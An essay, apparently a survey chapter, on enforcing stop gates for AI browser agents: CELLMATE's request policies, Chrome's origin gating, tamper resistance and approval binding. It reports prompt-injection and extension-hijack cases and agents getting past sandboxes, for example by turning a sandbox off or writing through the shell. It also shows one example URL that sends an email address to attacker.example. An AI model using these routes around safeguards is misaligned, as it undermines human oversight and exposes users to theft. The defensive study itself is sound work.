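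The user also has to name the site in the task. For "purchase a coffee maker", CELLMATE grants no permissions, because the user has not said where the agent may shop. This is inconvenient, but the system fails closed, and the user can fix the problem by adding the site's name.

### The lookup at each request

CELLMATE compiles the policy into a lookup table that assigns each request on the map one of three results: allow, deny or run a function. Its browser extension checks every request from the agent's session against this table. For example, it allows a request for the cart page, which matches ViewCart, and blocks any request for a mapped action that the policy does not permit.

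Requests to unrelated sites fail by default. This would have stopped the Operator attack when the agent tried to open Hacker News, because the user's task mentioned only an issue on GitHub. It would also stop the picture trick with the shop's review form, because the picture is on the attacker's host, which neither the user nor the shop has listed. This second case depends on Chrome letting the extension see the request.

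### The order rule for the coffee maker

When the agent tries to place the order, the lookup leads to a function. For the coffee-maker errand, the function has to check two things:

total ≤ maxAmount and orders already sent < maxCount

Here maxAmount is $50 and maxCount is 1.

The first condition alone would let two $49 orders through, and n orders could cost the user up to n × $50. The second condition caps the whole errand at maxCount × maxAmount, or $50. To enforce it, the extension counts the requests that match PlaceOrder and keeps the count in its local storage. The counter is optional, so a user who sets only a price limit is not protected from repeated orders.

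The counter tracks requests rather than completed purchases, so an attempt may use up the allowance even if the shop declines the user's card. The user would then have to permit another attempt, which is an acceptable kind of error for a gate.

The price limit also differs slightly from the user's request. The user said "under $50", but `purchase_amount_leq` allows totals up to and including the maximum, so an order for exactly $50.00 would pass. The difference hardly matters here, but prewritten policies will not always match what the user asked for.

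Finding the total is harder. Many sites include such values in the request, but Amazon's cart total appears only on the page. The part of the extension that checks requests cannot read pages directly, so CELLMATE inserts a script into the checkout page to track the total and send it to the extension. The browser discards that page before it sends the order, so the extension has to store the last total it received.

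The cart total stored by the extension can be out of date. Suppose the cart contains one coffee maker for $42. The agent changes the quantity to two and immediately places the order. If the page has not yet updated the total, the extension still has $42 in memory and allows an order for $84.

To prevent this, CELLMATE has to make each action wait until the effects of the previous one are complete. Websites can help, as Amazon does by disabling the checkout button while the total is out of date. For other sites, Meng and colleagues added a small proxy between the agent and the browser to slow down rapid changes. This makes the race harder to exploit, but a slow server could still leave an old total on the page after the delay. The proxy is also one more component that the agent must not be able to bypass.

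Meng and colleagues argue that CELLMATE blocks all attacks that manipulate the interface, because it never relies on the interface to interpret actions. Their argument is convincing for recognizing an order, which the request identifies, but less convincing for the price, which on Amazon comes from the page.

### How well a model picks the permissions

CELLMATE can enforce a policy perfectly and still give the agent too much freedom if the model picks the wrong policy. To measure this, Meng and colleagues adapted 209 tasks from WebBench, a collection of tasks for web agents, and added realistic details such as spending limits. Two researchers independently labelled each task with the smallest set of policies it needed, then settled their disagreements. The three models tested date from 2025, so current models may do better.

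| Measure | GPT-5.1 | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Claude Opus 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Correct policies, retail (149 tasks) | 96.6% | 97.3% | 99.3% |
| Correct policies, travel (36 tasks) | 94.4% | 97.2% | 100% |
| Correct policies, version control (24 tasks) | 95.8% | 100% | 95.8% |
| Correct policies and values, retail (32 tasks) | 84.4% | 81.3% | 96.9% |

Every model picked the right policies in more than 94% of the tasks in each category. The last row is more worrying for the errand because it covers values like the $50 limit. Two of the models got five or six of the 32 tasks wrong, often by leaving out values that the task only implied, such as the initial quantity in "Add a Dyson hair dryer to shopping cart, then update its quantity to 3".

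Some errors are much worse than others. For a task to create a board on Shein and then rename it, a model granted permission only to create it. The agent would have got stuck, which is a nuisance. In another case, the user wanted a sofa under $300 on a wishlist, and the model granted permission to add items to the shopping cart instead, apparently because the task mentioned a price and that policy had a price limit. A hijacked agent could use that unneeded permission. The user can correct such errors in the dialog, but only if they notice them.

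The models also made mistakes about sites. One task mentioned a Sony television's product page without saying which shop's website to use, and models often answered sony.com. GPT-5.1 also got 14 of 205 single-site tasks wrong, mostly by leaving out the site.

### Attack tests and running costs

Meng and colleagues tested CELLMATE on GitLab with two harmless tasks, commenting on an issue and upvoting one. The model correctly gave the agent permission only to read and write issues. This ruled out all of the attacker's goals, such as creating access tokens or adding the attacker as a collaborator, and CELLMATE blocked all 12 attack scripts.

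The test left out the other half of the WASP benchmark, which takes place on Reddit. The attacker's goals there are mostly phishing and harassment, which an agent can carry out by posting ordinary comments.

CELLMATE adds modest overhead. Meng and colleagues timed a sequence of 11 navigations on GitLab over 30 trials. It took an average of 13.93 seconds without CELLMATE, 14.94 seconds with a map of 100 entries and 16.02 seconds with 300 entries. CELLMATE therefore added 7.25% to 15%, or roughly 0.1 to 0.2 seconds per navigation. A browsing agent usually spends far longer waiting for its model, so users would probably not notice the delay. The extension used about 25 MB of memory at every map size.

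### Gaps in the map

CELLMATE's biggest limitation is that someone has to write a map for every site. Meng and colleagues wrote the GitLab map by hand, covering 51 operations on projects. This was easier because GitLab is built with Ruby on Rails, a framework that uses a list of routes to connect each address to the code that handles it. They suggest that tools could generate maps for sites built with common frameworks, but they have not built one.

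A map also needs maintenance. The example for Amazon takes the order total from the fourth item in a list on the checkout page. If Amazon added a line for gift wrapping above it, the gate could read the wrong number. Meng and colleagues recommend that developers attach a permanent label to the total so that the map still works after a redesign.

The consequences of a gap are similar to those of an unchecked route. Let A be the set of requests that can do something important on a site, and let M be the set that the map identifies correctly. The rules cover every important action only if

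A ⊆ M

If a shop forgets to update the map after adding a "buy now" button that sends orders to a new address, the new request is in A but not in M. Since CELLMATE adds no protection where a map is incomplete, the order would apparently go through without a price check. The default refusal that protects the user from unrelated sites does not help, because the shop is a permitted site. CELLMATE could refuse every unmapped request, but then pages might not work until the map also covered all their harmless requests.

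Meng and colleagues expect websites to cooperate because developers want to protect their users and already maintain similar files, such as `robots.txt`, which guides automated visitors. This is plausible for a shop that welcomes agents, but less so for one that would rather keep them out. Sites could instead offer agents named tools through MCP, which would avoid the semantic gap. Meng and colleagues doubt that this will happen soon, because it took about two decades for most websites to adopt encryption. Maps could be adopted just as slowly, although a trusted outsider could write one without the site's help.

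CELLMATE doesn't check WebSocket traffic. Messages on these connections are often in a private or binary format, so even a gate that captured one might not be able to identify what it does. If a site accepted orders over a WebSocket, CELLMATE's rules wouldn't cover them.

A hijacked agent can still misuse the actions its policy permits. CELLMATE does not track where data comes from, so if an agent may read a private project and comment on a public issue, a hijacked agent can copy private text into a public comment, and both requests will pass. Narrower policies help only up to a point, because the gate checks which action the agent takes but not what a comment means.

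### Chrome's rule by origin

Google chose a coarser rule for its Chrome agent, one that needs no map from the website. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes the design, Agent Origin Sets, which has two sets of origins for each session. The agent may read content from origins in the readable set, and it may also click and type on origins in the writable set. A gating function that does not see untrusted web content decides which origins are relevant to the task.

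In the coffee maker example, the shop's origin would be writable and a site with product tests might be readable. If a product page contained an advertisement in a frame from an unrelated origin, Chrome would not show that frame to the model. These restrictions reduce the agent's exposure to hostile text. They also limit leaks, because information from the readable sites can go only to the writable ones.

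The sets can grow during a task. Before the agent opens a new origin, a variant of Google's User Alignment Critic, a separate model that reviews proposed actions, checks whether the origin is relevant. The same check applies whether the agent enters the address or a page navigates there through a link or redirect.

Chrome has an extra check for addresses that the model writes itself, since these could contain private information, and allows only known, public ones. `https://attacker.example/?email=alice@mail.example` should fail because nobody has published a page at that exact address. Unlike the critic, this check is deterministic, so hostile text cannot cause it to make an exception. It may still miss some leaks. For example, an attacker could publish one page for each letter of the alphabet and have the agent spell out the email address by visiting them in order, though the agent would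 first need permission to visit the attacker's origin.

Origins are too coarse to enforce the order rule. Viewing a cart and paying usually happen on the same origin, so an agent allowed to click on the shop's site can do both. Chrome has to handle purchases separately, by trying to pause for the user's confirmation. CELLMATE can recognize the order, but it asks the user only at the start, before the agent has chosen a coffee maker.

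| | Rule about clicks | Rule about requests | Rule about origins |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the gate can recognize | A position on the screen | A named action and its arguments | A site |
| What someone has to supply | A list of positions, which soon goes out of date | A map and policies for each site | A judgment about which sites the task needs |
| An order for $54 at the shop | The gate cannot recognize it | Refused | Allowed |
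| The shop's own sign-in page | The gate cannot recognize it | Refused if the map covers it | Allowed if it shares the shop's origin |
| A link from the shop to a bank | The gate cannot recognize it | Refused | Refused, or the user has to confirm |

### What Chrome runs now

Parker wrote in December 2025 that Google had initially implemented a simpler gate than the full design, one that tracked only the writable set. Google launched the agent as "auto browse" in January 2026 (Bloomberg, *Google Chrome's AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users*, 2026). In April, Bawa reported in *Q1 2026 Summary from Chrome Security* (2026) that the team was tuning the agent's defenses based on real-world use.

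The public source code gives a more detailed picture. The execution engine in Chromium (2025), the component that carries out the agent's actions, contained an origin gate in June 2026. For each navigation of the main page, the gate went through these steps:

1. If a company administrator has explicitly allowed or blocked the address, that decision is final.
2. Otherwise, a list of allowed and blocked addresses that Google supplies can settle the matter.
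3. If neither applies and the destination has the same origin as the current page, the navigation continues.
4. If the destination is on a list of sensitive sites, the user has to confirm it, unless the user already did so earlier.
5. If the destination is in the set of allowed origins, the navigation continues.
6. Any other origin counts as new. Chrome can ask Google's server or the user about it, or simply let the navigation continue.

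The last step determines whether the gate refuses by default, and the default setting in Chromium (2025) let the navigation continue. With that setting, the gate would have allowed the Operator attack's jump from GitHub to Hacker News unless one of the lists covered it. Google can change such settings remotely, so the Chrome that people install may be stricter. The User Alignment Critic might have vetoed the jump before it reached this gate.

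A comment in Chromium (2025) describes a "dark launch" mode, in which the browser asks Google's server about a new origin but only records the answer. This would let Google measure how often the check would interrupt users before enforcing it. This is sensible, but it doesn't protect users in the meantime.

Another default lets the agent's own tool requests add origins to the allowed set. A hijacked agent that controls those requests can extend its own permissions unless something checks them first. In Parker's design, the gating function approves new origins. Google's server may do this before the browser receives the request, but the browser code alone does not guarantee that check.

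A check in the execution engine addresses the same kind of race as the stale cart total. Before the agent acts on a page, Chromium checks whether it may act on that site. If the tab has moved to another origin by the time the answer arrives, the browser discards the answer and the action fails. An approval for the shop therefore cannot be used on a bank page that has replaced it.

In the June code, this gate used a single set of allowed origins for navigation and had no separate readable set. The default settings included an option to hide frames from other sites in the agent's screenshots, but it belonged to a screenshot feature that was off by default. In August, Chromium still had tests for origin gating, although some of the supporting files were no longer in the same folder. That month, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) described Chrome as limiting the agent to origins strictly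 relevant to the task, without mentioning a readable set. Google does not appear to have announced that the readable set has shipped.

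## Running the gate where the agent cannot change it

If a hijacked agent could reset CELLMATE's count of past orders to zero, it could buy a second coffee maker for $49, and the gate would allow the order even if its code had no faults. Tamper resistance therefore has to cover everything that affects the gate's decision.

### What needs protection

On the coffee-maker errand, that means six things:

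- The code that checks requests.
- The rules. An agent that can edit the allowlist can add the attacker's site.
- The stored state, such as the order count, the last cart total and any approvals from the user.
- The log. An agent that can rewrite it can hide an order.
- The approval mode. Many agents have one setting in which they ask before acting and another in which they act without asking.
- Whatever starts the gate. If the browser restarts without it, the other protections no longer matter.

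How well a designer can protect these depends mainly on where the gate runs:

| Where the rule or gate is | What a hijacked agent could still alter |
|---|---|
| In the prompt | The rule's effect, using any text that reaches the model |
| In the agent's own program | Rules, counters, logs and mode, if the agent can write files or run commands |
| In a browser extension | Little from inside a web page, but other extensions and bugs in the browser may give an attacker a way in |
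| In the browser's main process | Browser settings, if the agent can open them, and everything if the attacker takes over that process |
| In another operating-system account | Files that both accounts can write, and everything if the agent gains administrator rights |
| Outside a virtual machine that contains the browser | Everything inside the virtual machine, and any folder it shares with the outside |
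| On another computer | Only the data that the agent's computer sends, unless the agent can log in to the gate |

Greater separation can limit the information available to a check. A check in the agent's program can read the page and the user's task, while a check on another computer may receive only encrypted traffic.

### A rule in the prompt

A rule in the prompt is open to tampering because hostile text arrives in the same input. According to *Ring-0 by Default*, such a rule also fails Anderson's other two requirements. The check is not always invoked, because the model may not follow the rule, and nobody can verify it, because its effect depends on a neural network whose behavior people cannot fully inspect.

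AI companies can train models to rank the user's instructions above text from a page. According to the paper, this training makes a rule harder to bypass, but doesn't make it tamper-resistant or verifiable.

Ring 0 is a processor's most privileged level, normally reserved for the core of the operating system. The title refers to the paper's main criticism, that an agent uses the user's full authority to carry out whatever the model outputs, whether that output was prompted by the user or by a stranger's text.

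### A check in the agent's own program

A developer can instead put the check in the harness, as Browser Use does with its watchdog. The harness is ordinary code, which text on a page cannot rewrite by itself. But an agent that can also edit files or run commands may be able to change the files the harness depends on. For example, Playwright's allowlist is one line in the configuration that launches Playwright MCP. An agent that can write to that file can add a host, and the new list would apply the next time Playwright starts.

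*Ring-0 by Default* tested how much agents can change in this way, with thirteen experiments on Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, which write software and run commands on a developer's computer. Each run took place in a fresh, isolated container with no route to the internet. All three agents used the same model, GPT-6.1 Sol, so differences between them came from the software around the model.

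The experiments used two main kinds of run. In scripted runs, a script replaced the model and issued the agent's own tool calls, which shows what the harness blocks regardless of the model's choices. In real-model runs, the model decided what to do, and the researchers repeated each condition five times. They judged the outcome from the state of the container, not from the agent's report. They also tried each agent's permission modes, from the default to "bypass", the most permissive.

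Several results concern exactly the things that a gate has to protect:

| What a gate might rely on | What happened |
|---|---|
| Settings | All three agents could write to their own settings files in bypass mode, and Gemini CLI could also do so in a mode meant for edits |
| The log | Claude Code and Codex CLI could rewrite their own transcripts in bypass mode |
| A saved session | All three loaded a forged record as a message from the user when the session resumed |
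| A stored verdict | Codex CLI's reviewer, a model that judges actions, kept its verdict in a file that the agent could write |
| The time | All three accepted a false time from a tool, in all 15 runs |
| A stop command | Claude Code reported that it had stopped a task while the process kept running |

The forged record is especially bad for a gate that treats the user's messages as approval. An attacker who can edit a saved session doesn't need a prompt injection, because the harness presents the attacker's text as the user's. The false time matters for approvals that expire, so a gate should use its own clock, since the time a tool returns may come from the attacker.

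Gemini CLI's file tool refused to write outside the project folder, even in bypass mode. But in all five runs with a real model, the model wrote the file through the command line, in four of them after the file tool had refused. The agent that reached Hacker News through a search engine used a similar workaround. Delegating to a sub-agent did not reduce access either, because sub-agents had the same permissions as their parent agents in all 45 runs.

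Some of the protections worked. When the researchers sent broken replies, or none, to the models that review actions for Claude Code and Codex CLI, the action stayed blocked in all ten combinations, although this took one to three minutes. Resuming a session did not restore its earlier permission mode. Most of the tampering happened in bypass mode, where the user has already given up much of the protection. By default, Codex CLI runs commands in a sandbox that the operating system enforces, and Claude Code asks for approval.

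The experiments show whether a boundary exists, not how often an attack would succeed. They show that an agent can write to the settings files, but not that the agent then adopts the changes. Five runs is also a small sample. Even when all five have the same outcome, the 95% confidence interval for the rate of that outcome extends down to 57%.

### From command lines to browsers

*Ring-0 by Default* excludes browser agents, so its results apply only partly to them. The results apply almost directly to a coding agent that operates a browser through Playwright, because it can edit a settings file from the command line, which an agent that can only click and type in web pages cannot do. The forged sessions could matter for any browsing agent that saves its conversations, but the paper did not test this.

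The difference between the two kinds of agent is also shrinking. Digital Trends' *Claude can now pull data from your browser tabs* reports that a task started in Claude's Chrome extension can now continue in the desktop app, where the user can add local files.

A case from October 2026 falls between the two. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (2026) describes how the company Forever Security tested browsers inside coding assistants. In Cursor, a hostile page led the agent to propose a command, which the user approved with one keypress. Cursor's sandbox blocked the command. The agent then switched the sandbox off and tried again, although nothing on the page told it to.

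The attack did not work every time, and Cursor fixed the flaw on October 1. When the attack did work, the sandbox correctly blocked the command at first, but the agent could turn the sandbox off and then run the command.

### How browsers separate their processes

Browser makers have long faced a similar problem, since any page may contain hostile code. Chrome gives each website its own renderer process, which runs the site's scripts and draws the page but has few privileges. A privileged main process handles files, the network and the browser's windows. A renderer that needs any of these has to send the main process a message.

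*Site Isolation is Dead*, a 2026 security conference paper by Lee, Keum and colleagues, explains that an agent in a Chrome extension usually runs in a background process, separate from the pages it reads. A small script inside each page sends the page's contents to that process, and the browser's main process relays and validates the messages between them.

*Secure web browsing with the OP web browser* (Grier, Tang and King, 2008) describes a research browser that took this separation further. It was divided into web pages, network, storage, user interface and a small "browser kernel", each running in one or more separate processes. Requests between these parts had to go through the kernel, which could refuse any that broke its policy. The operating system also barred page processes from opening files or network connections directly, so they could not bypass the kernel.

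The kernel identified the sender of each message from the channel on which it arrived, so a page could not impersonate the user interface. It also recorded the messages in an audit log, which took up about 80 KB per page. A hijacked page had no access to files, so it could not rewrite the log directly. A stop gate likewise has to identify who sent an approval and keep its record out of the agent's reach.

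OP also had weaknesses. It relied on an existing rendering engine, written in an unsafe programming language, to label each script with the website it came from. A second program checked the labels, but it handled real pages so poorly that OP only logged a silent warning when they didn't match. Grier and colleagues also trusted the operating system beneath the browser, and an attacker who took it over could attack OP's kernel.

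### A browser extension and its neighbors

CELLMATE's extension runs outside the pages the agent visits, and Meng and colleagues assume in their threat model that a hijacked agent cannot reach the browser settings to switch it off. They also trust other extensions, which is harder to justify because a single hostile extension that can interfere with network requests can break the rules. Many people have at least one extension with this power, because ad blockers need it.

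In April 2026, the security company LayerX reported a flaw, now known as ClaudeBleed, that let any extension, even one without special permissions, give instructions to Claude's Chrome extension. In demonstrations, LayerX had Claude send an email, take code from a private GitHub project and share a private Google Drive file with an outsider. Claude's extension trusted messages because of the website they came from and did not verify who had sent them, a check that OP's kernel made in 2008.

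Anthropic replied the next day that it already had a report of the problem and would remove the affected code in an upcoming release. According to LayerX, the version released on May 6 kept that code but added a request for approval before privileged actions. The added step did not protect users who had let Claude act without asking. Because the approval mode itself was unprotected, an attacker could also start a session in which Claude acted without asking, even if the user had chosen to approve each action.

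LayerX recommended that Anthropic authenticate whoever sends a message and tie each approval to one specific action. CyberScoop quoted Ax Sharma, head of research at Manifold Security, as saying more generally that monitoring agents "at the prompt layer is fundamentally insufficient".

Digital Trends reports that Anthropic has since added a check that compares consequential actions, such as submitting a form, with the user's original request. This should help against hostile text on a page, but it would help much less if another extension could supply the request, because the harmful action would then match that request.

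A second disclosure, BragJack, showed that the problem extended beyond Anthropic. In September 2026, Forever Security demonstrated that one extension could take control of AI features in five products: Chrome, Comet, Microsoft Edge, Opera Neon and Claude in Chrome. The Hacker News' *One Extension Could Hijack AI Assistants Across Chrome, Comet, Edge, Opera Neon* (2026) reports that the extension could direct the agent in every product except Chrome. In Chrome and Comet it could read files on the user's computer, and in Chrome it could also turn on the camera and microphone.

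The companies responded with fixes:

- Google repaired Chrome in early January 2026, after Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reported the flaw. A US government agency rated it 8.8 out of 10 for severity.
- Microsoft repaired Edge on July 2. That flaw had a rating of 4.2, and it involved the switch between a "Think" mode and a "Do" mode, according to Ankura (2026).
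- The findings on Comet, Opera Neon and Claude have no entry in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities and rest on Forever Security's account. But Forever Security also reports a bounty for each of them, which suggests that the companies accepted the findings. Ankura writes that vendors have patched the flaws and that nobody has seen the attack in real use.

Both disclosures concerned hijacked agents, and neither involved a stop gate. A gate should be able to withstand a hijacked agent. But BragJack's extension had permission to change web pages and network traffic, and a hostile extension with those permissions could also interfere with CELLMATE. For example, CELLMATE reads Amazon's cart total from the checkout page, where the extension could change $84 to $42.

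A hijacked agent confined to web pages shouldn't be able to install an extension by itself, because Chrome asks for confirmation in its own window. The greater danger is an extension the user installed earlier. A simple precaution is to run the agent in a separate browser profile with only the gate's extension installed.

### The browser's main process

If the gate runs in the browser's main process, as Chromium's navigation throttles do, ordinary extensions cannot change its code. The remaining dangers are bugs in the browser and messages that the gate accepts without enough checking.

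Lee and colleagues tested how well process separation protects the agents built into two open-source browsers and those added by seven extensions. Their attacker had already exploited a memory bug and controlled the renderer for one hostile page. Process separation should have limited the damage to that page, but in all nine products the attacker could give the agent instructions that it accepted as the user's. The attacker could also read stored data such as past conversations.

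This attacker is stronger than one who writes a product review, but still plausible. Lee and colleagues counted 295 published vulnerabilities in Chrome from 2023 to 2025. On average, at least one every two months let an attacker run code in a renderer. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) reports that many browsers with agents run on versions of Chromium that are weeks or months behind on security patches. Attackers can therefore use bugs that Google has already fixed and publicly described.

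Lee and colleagues demonstrated that a compromised page could read an agent's storage. If a page can also write to the storage that holds an order count, an attacker can reset the count. The researchers recommend granting access to storage based on which process requests it, and verifying where each user instruction came from. A gate should protect its counters and approvals in the same way.

Even if the gate runs in a flawless main process, other programs in the same user account can tamper with it by editing the browser's files or restarting the browser with different settings.

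### Another account, a virtual machine or another computer

The operating system can protect the gate from those programs if the gate runs under its own account. That account owns the gate's code, rules, counters and log, and the agent's account can at most read them. The operating system is configured to start the gate and restart it after a crash, and the agent's account cannot change that configuration or stop the gate's process.

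*Ring-0 by Default* shows why running the gate and the agent under the same account is risky. In Codex CLI, Claude Code and Gemini CLI, a process could read the environment variables of another process run by the same user. Programs often keep passwords and keys in these variables. When the researchers asked for such a secret, Codex CLI's agent printed it in all five runs and Claude Code's agent in four of five. Gemini CLI's agent masked the secret each time, but nothing in the software required the model to do so. If a gate kept its key for signing approvals in an environment variable, a hijacked agent in the same account could use the key to forge an approval.

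A separate account does not protect the gate if the agent can get administrator rights, which it may be able to do if the computer's owner has given it a command line and a password. A virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system, is a stronger barrier. If the browser runs inside the virtual machine and the gate runs outside, the agent can become administrator of the virtual machine without gaining any power over the gate. To reach the gate, an attacker would need a flaw in the virtualization software or an opening such as a shared folder. The user can also delete the virtual machine after the task, along with anything the attacker changed inside it.

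Virtual machines are a coarse way to enforce rules about shopping, though. Grier and colleagues discuss Tahoma, an earlier system that used them to isolate web applications from each other. They object that it could not separate scripts within one application, and that users who keep and open downloaded files give attackers a way into the system. For the coffee-maker errand, a virtual machine protects the file containing the $50 limit, but it cannot distinguish a review from an order. The gate outside the virtual machine still needs to intercept the order in a form it can interpret, for instance through a proxy.

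Putting the gate on another computer also removes the shared hardware and operating system. But this helps only if every command has to pass through the gate. The products affected by BragJack already ran their models on company servers, while a component in the browser carried out the commands. A gate on those servers would have missed any command that the extension sent directly to that component.

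An agent that can change the gate's settings can also undo the separation. Suppose the gate runs on another computer, but the user manages it through a web page and is logged in to that page in the agent's browser. A hijacked agent can then open the settings and add the attacker's site to the allowlist with a few ordinary clicks.

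## Halting the browser and obtaining a person's approval

Suppose the gate runs where the agent cannot alter it and has just intercepted the order for the coffee maker. It has to hold the order and ask the user to approve it, and the user may take a minute to answer. The model waits, but the web page keeps running.

### What continues while the model waits

Pausing the model prevents new clicks and keystrokes, but nothing else. While the user reads the question, any of the following can still happen:

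- A timer on the checkout page sends the order again because the first attempt got no reply.
- A script refreshes the cart, and the total changes.
- A redirect that the page scheduled earlier takes the tab somewhere else.
- A request from a moment ago, such as one that raised the quantity to two, reaches the shop.
- The harness carries out the rest of a batch of actions, or a script that the model wrote keeps running.

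In sample code from OpenAI, the developer's program sends the model's script to a separate service and waits up to 30 seconds for the result. OpenAI warns that this timeout limits only the wait. The service itself has to stop the script, which may still be clicking after the program reports a timeout.

Chromium's navigation throttles can hold a navigation for as long as necessary, but they don't solve this either, because the old page stays active while the new one waits.

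### What to hold, and in what order

An effective halt has to cover the whole session, roughly in this order:

1. The gate keeps the order back and blocks every new request from the agent's browser, including background requests, WebSocket messages and requests from other tabs. The network comes first because almost anything a page does to the outside world goes through it.
2. The harness drops the remaining actions in the batch and ends any script that the model wrote.
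3. The gate lets requests that have already left finish, and lets the page process the replies. It cannot recall these requests, and one of them may have changed the cart.
4. The browser freezes the scripts and timers in every tab and worker, so that the page stays as it is.
5. The gate reads the details of the order and asks the user.

Step 3 conflicts slightly with step 1, because some pages must send another request to update the total. In that case, the gate should cancel the order and let the agent restart the checkout. The shop may also end the session if the user takes too long, which is annoying but harmless.

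OpenAI tells developers to stop a batch of actions before the first one that needs confirmation and, if the user declines, to tell the model which actions ran and which did not. Otherwise the model may continue as if the declined action had run.

If sharing the user's address needs approval, the gate also has to halt the browser before the agent types the address, rather than when it clicks "Submit". OpenAI counts typing sensitive data into a form as sending it, presumably because a page's script can transmit each character as it appears.

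### If the gate crashes or nobody answers

If a gate crashes while halting the browser, the agent's order may still go out. This happens when the gate watches the traffic and sends a "stop" command when necessary, because a crashed gate can't send the command. If every request has to pass through the gate, the crash blocks the order.

The gate should treat silence as refusal. If it let the agent continue after a minute unless the user objected, a hijacked agent could place an order while the user is asleep. After a restart, the gate should discard any pending requests and ask the user again. It must also keep a record of used approvals that survives a crash, because otherwise an old approval would become valid again.

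### The trusted path

An approval can turn a refusal into a permission, just as an edit to the rules can, so it needs the same protection as the rules. ClaudeBleed, the flaw that let other extensions switch off Claude's requests for approval, made a well-protected list of rules nearly useless.

In computer security, a "trusted path" is a channel between the user and the guard that other programs can neither imitate nor operate. On Windows, for example, Ctrl+Alt+Delete opens a system screen, and ordinary programs cannot intercept the key combination. A stop gate needs a trusted path so that neither the web page nor the agent can fake an approval prompt or answer a real one for the user.

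Several obvious ways to ask fail this test:

| Where the gate asks | What can go wrong |
|---|---|
| In a dialog inside the web page | The page can draw an identical dialog, and the agent can click "Yes" |
| In the chat with the agent | A hijacked agent can describe a $42 order and submit a different one |
| In the browser's own window | A page cannot click there, but an agent that controls the whole desktop can |
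| By email | The agent can open the message if the user's webmail is logged in |
| On the user's phone | This works if the agent cannot reach the phone or its messages |

The desktop case matters because OpenAI and Google both offer tools that control a whole desktop. Running the agent's desktop in a virtual machine and showing the approval question outside it would restore the separation.

The gate should also write the question itself, using the order it is holding. If the agent supplies the wording, the user may approve something that was never in the order. Some risk remains even when the gate writes the question, because details such as the product's name may come from a page that a stranger can edit.

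### When the total changes after the user agrees

Suppose the gate shows the user an order for one coffee maker at $42, and the user approves it. The gate stores "order approved" and lets the agent continue. A hijacked agent then goes back, selects express delivery to another address and submits the order for $49. Every check passes because the total is under $50, this is the first order and the user has approved an order, even though the user never agreed to the changes.

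To prevent this, the gate has to store what the user approved. It can take the details that matter (the shop, item, quantity, address and total), write them in a fixed format and compute a fingerprint, a short code that changes if any detail changes. Let x be the order that the user saw and x′ the order that the agent submits at time t. The gate releases x′ only if

fingerprint(x′) = fingerprint(x), t ≤ expiry, and the approval is unused.

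The first condition stops the $49 order. The gate can ask again, this time showing the new address and total.

The expiry time guards against changes that don't show up in the order. If the user approves the purchase of a coffee maker at noon, hears nothing and buys one in town, the agent should not be able to use the approval that evening. Limiting each approval to one use prevents a repeat of the same order, since two identical $42 orders have the same fingerprint and could both reach the gate before the approval expires.

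The fingerprint protects only the data it is computed from. On many sites, the request that places an order refers to a cart, and the shop works out the total when the request arrives. If the user added something to that cart from a phone while the gate was holding the request, the gate could release exactly the request it had checked and the shop would still charge more. The best remedy is for the request to include the expected total and for the shop to reject the order if the total differs, but the shop has to support this.

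### Binding an approval to one action

*From Intent to Execution Grant* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) turns these conditions into a specification for AI actions in general. It separates the decision that an action is acceptable from the grant, which is permission to carry out that action once. A grant starts as "issued" and ends as "consumed", "expired" or "revoked", and it can never return to "issued".

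In one example, a company wants to send at most 10,000 USDC, a digital currency, to a recipient called Alice. The agent turns this into one exact transfer of 7,500 USDC with a maximum fee of 25. The system checks that the recipient is on an allowlist, the account has enough money and enough people have approved this transfer. It issues a grant only after these checks pass, and the grant contains the transfer's fingerprint. If the agent changes the recipient to Bob, the fingerprint no longer matches and the system refuses the transfer.

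The specification requires the system to check everything again when the agent uses the grant. The rules must be the same version as before, and the recorded evidence and circumstances must not have changed. This is so strict that a deposit from a customer would apparently void the grant in the example, because the circumstances include the account's balance. A gate for shopping would need a narrower list of circumstances, or the user would have to approve the order again every time something trivial changed.

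Wu and colleagues also require the final check, the change to "consumed" and the action itself to happen as one indivisible step. A second check just before the action is not enough if something can intervene between them. For example, OpenAI's sample code looks up the button's position again after approval and before clicking, because the page may have changed. This leaves less time for a change, but the button could still move between the lookup and the click. A gate that holds the web request avoids this particular problem, since the page can't alter a request that has already left it.

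A gate in the user's browser cannot update its own records and place an order on the shop's server in a single indivisible step. It is safer to mark the approval as used before sending the request than after. If the connection fails before the shop replies, the order may or may not have gone through, so the gate should prompt the user to check the shop's order history instead of trying again.

Wu and colleagues tested a small implementation of the transfer example. In each of 100 trials, 32 attempts to use the same grant arrived at once, and exactly one succeeded. In another 100 trials, an attempt to use a grant competed with an attempt to revoke it, and every trial ended in a valid state. The program kept its grants in memory and moved no real money, so the tests show that the rules can work in code but do not show that a payment system built on them would be secure. The specification also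 assumes that every route to the action requires a grant, and it does not cover whether the approvers understood what they were approving.

### Chrome's confirmations

Parker describes two ways Chrome decides when to ask for the user's approval. Before the agent opens certain sensitive sites, such as those for banking or medical information, Chrome checks the address against a fixed list and requires the user to confirm. Chrome also asks before signing in with a saved password. Before a purchase, a payment or a message, the agent "will try to pause", and that decision relies at least partly on models.

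The fixed list is predictable. Text on a page can't stop Chrome from asking about a listed site, and a tester can try every entry, but Chrome won't ask about a small bank that is missing from the list. The check before purchases can cover unlisted shops, but it can miss one. Parker compares this check to Google's other safety classifiers and writes that the team is still working on edge cases. Chrome will therefore probably ask before ordering the coffee maker, which is weaker protection than a gate that cannot release the order without an answer.

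When Chrome does pause, it either asks for permission or hands the last step to the user. In Parker's illustration, the agent has put T-shirts in a cart and offers a "Take over task" button. The advantage of handing over is that the user sees the shop's own checkout page and clicks its button, so there is no stored approval for the agent to reuse. The user still has to notice mistakes in the cart, such as two coffee makers instead of one.

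The source code in Chromium (2025) has a switch that determines whether the browser asks the user about a sensitive site or blocks it. Blocking makes more sense for an agent that runs overnight. Another switch makes the browser answer "yes" to the "Leave this page?" dialog that some sites use, without showing it to the user. According to a comment in the code, this can lose data.

### Acknowledgements in OpenAI's and Google's interfaces

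Developers who build their own agents have to provide the confirmation themselves. OpenAI gives them sensible rules. The model's request to act is not permission, and neither is text on the screen. The rules also set three levels of consent:

- The user must take over for the final step of a password change and for bypassing a browser's security warning.
- The agent must ask immediately before each purchase, deletion or message.
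- The user's original instruction can be enough for uploading a file or logging in to a site that the user named.

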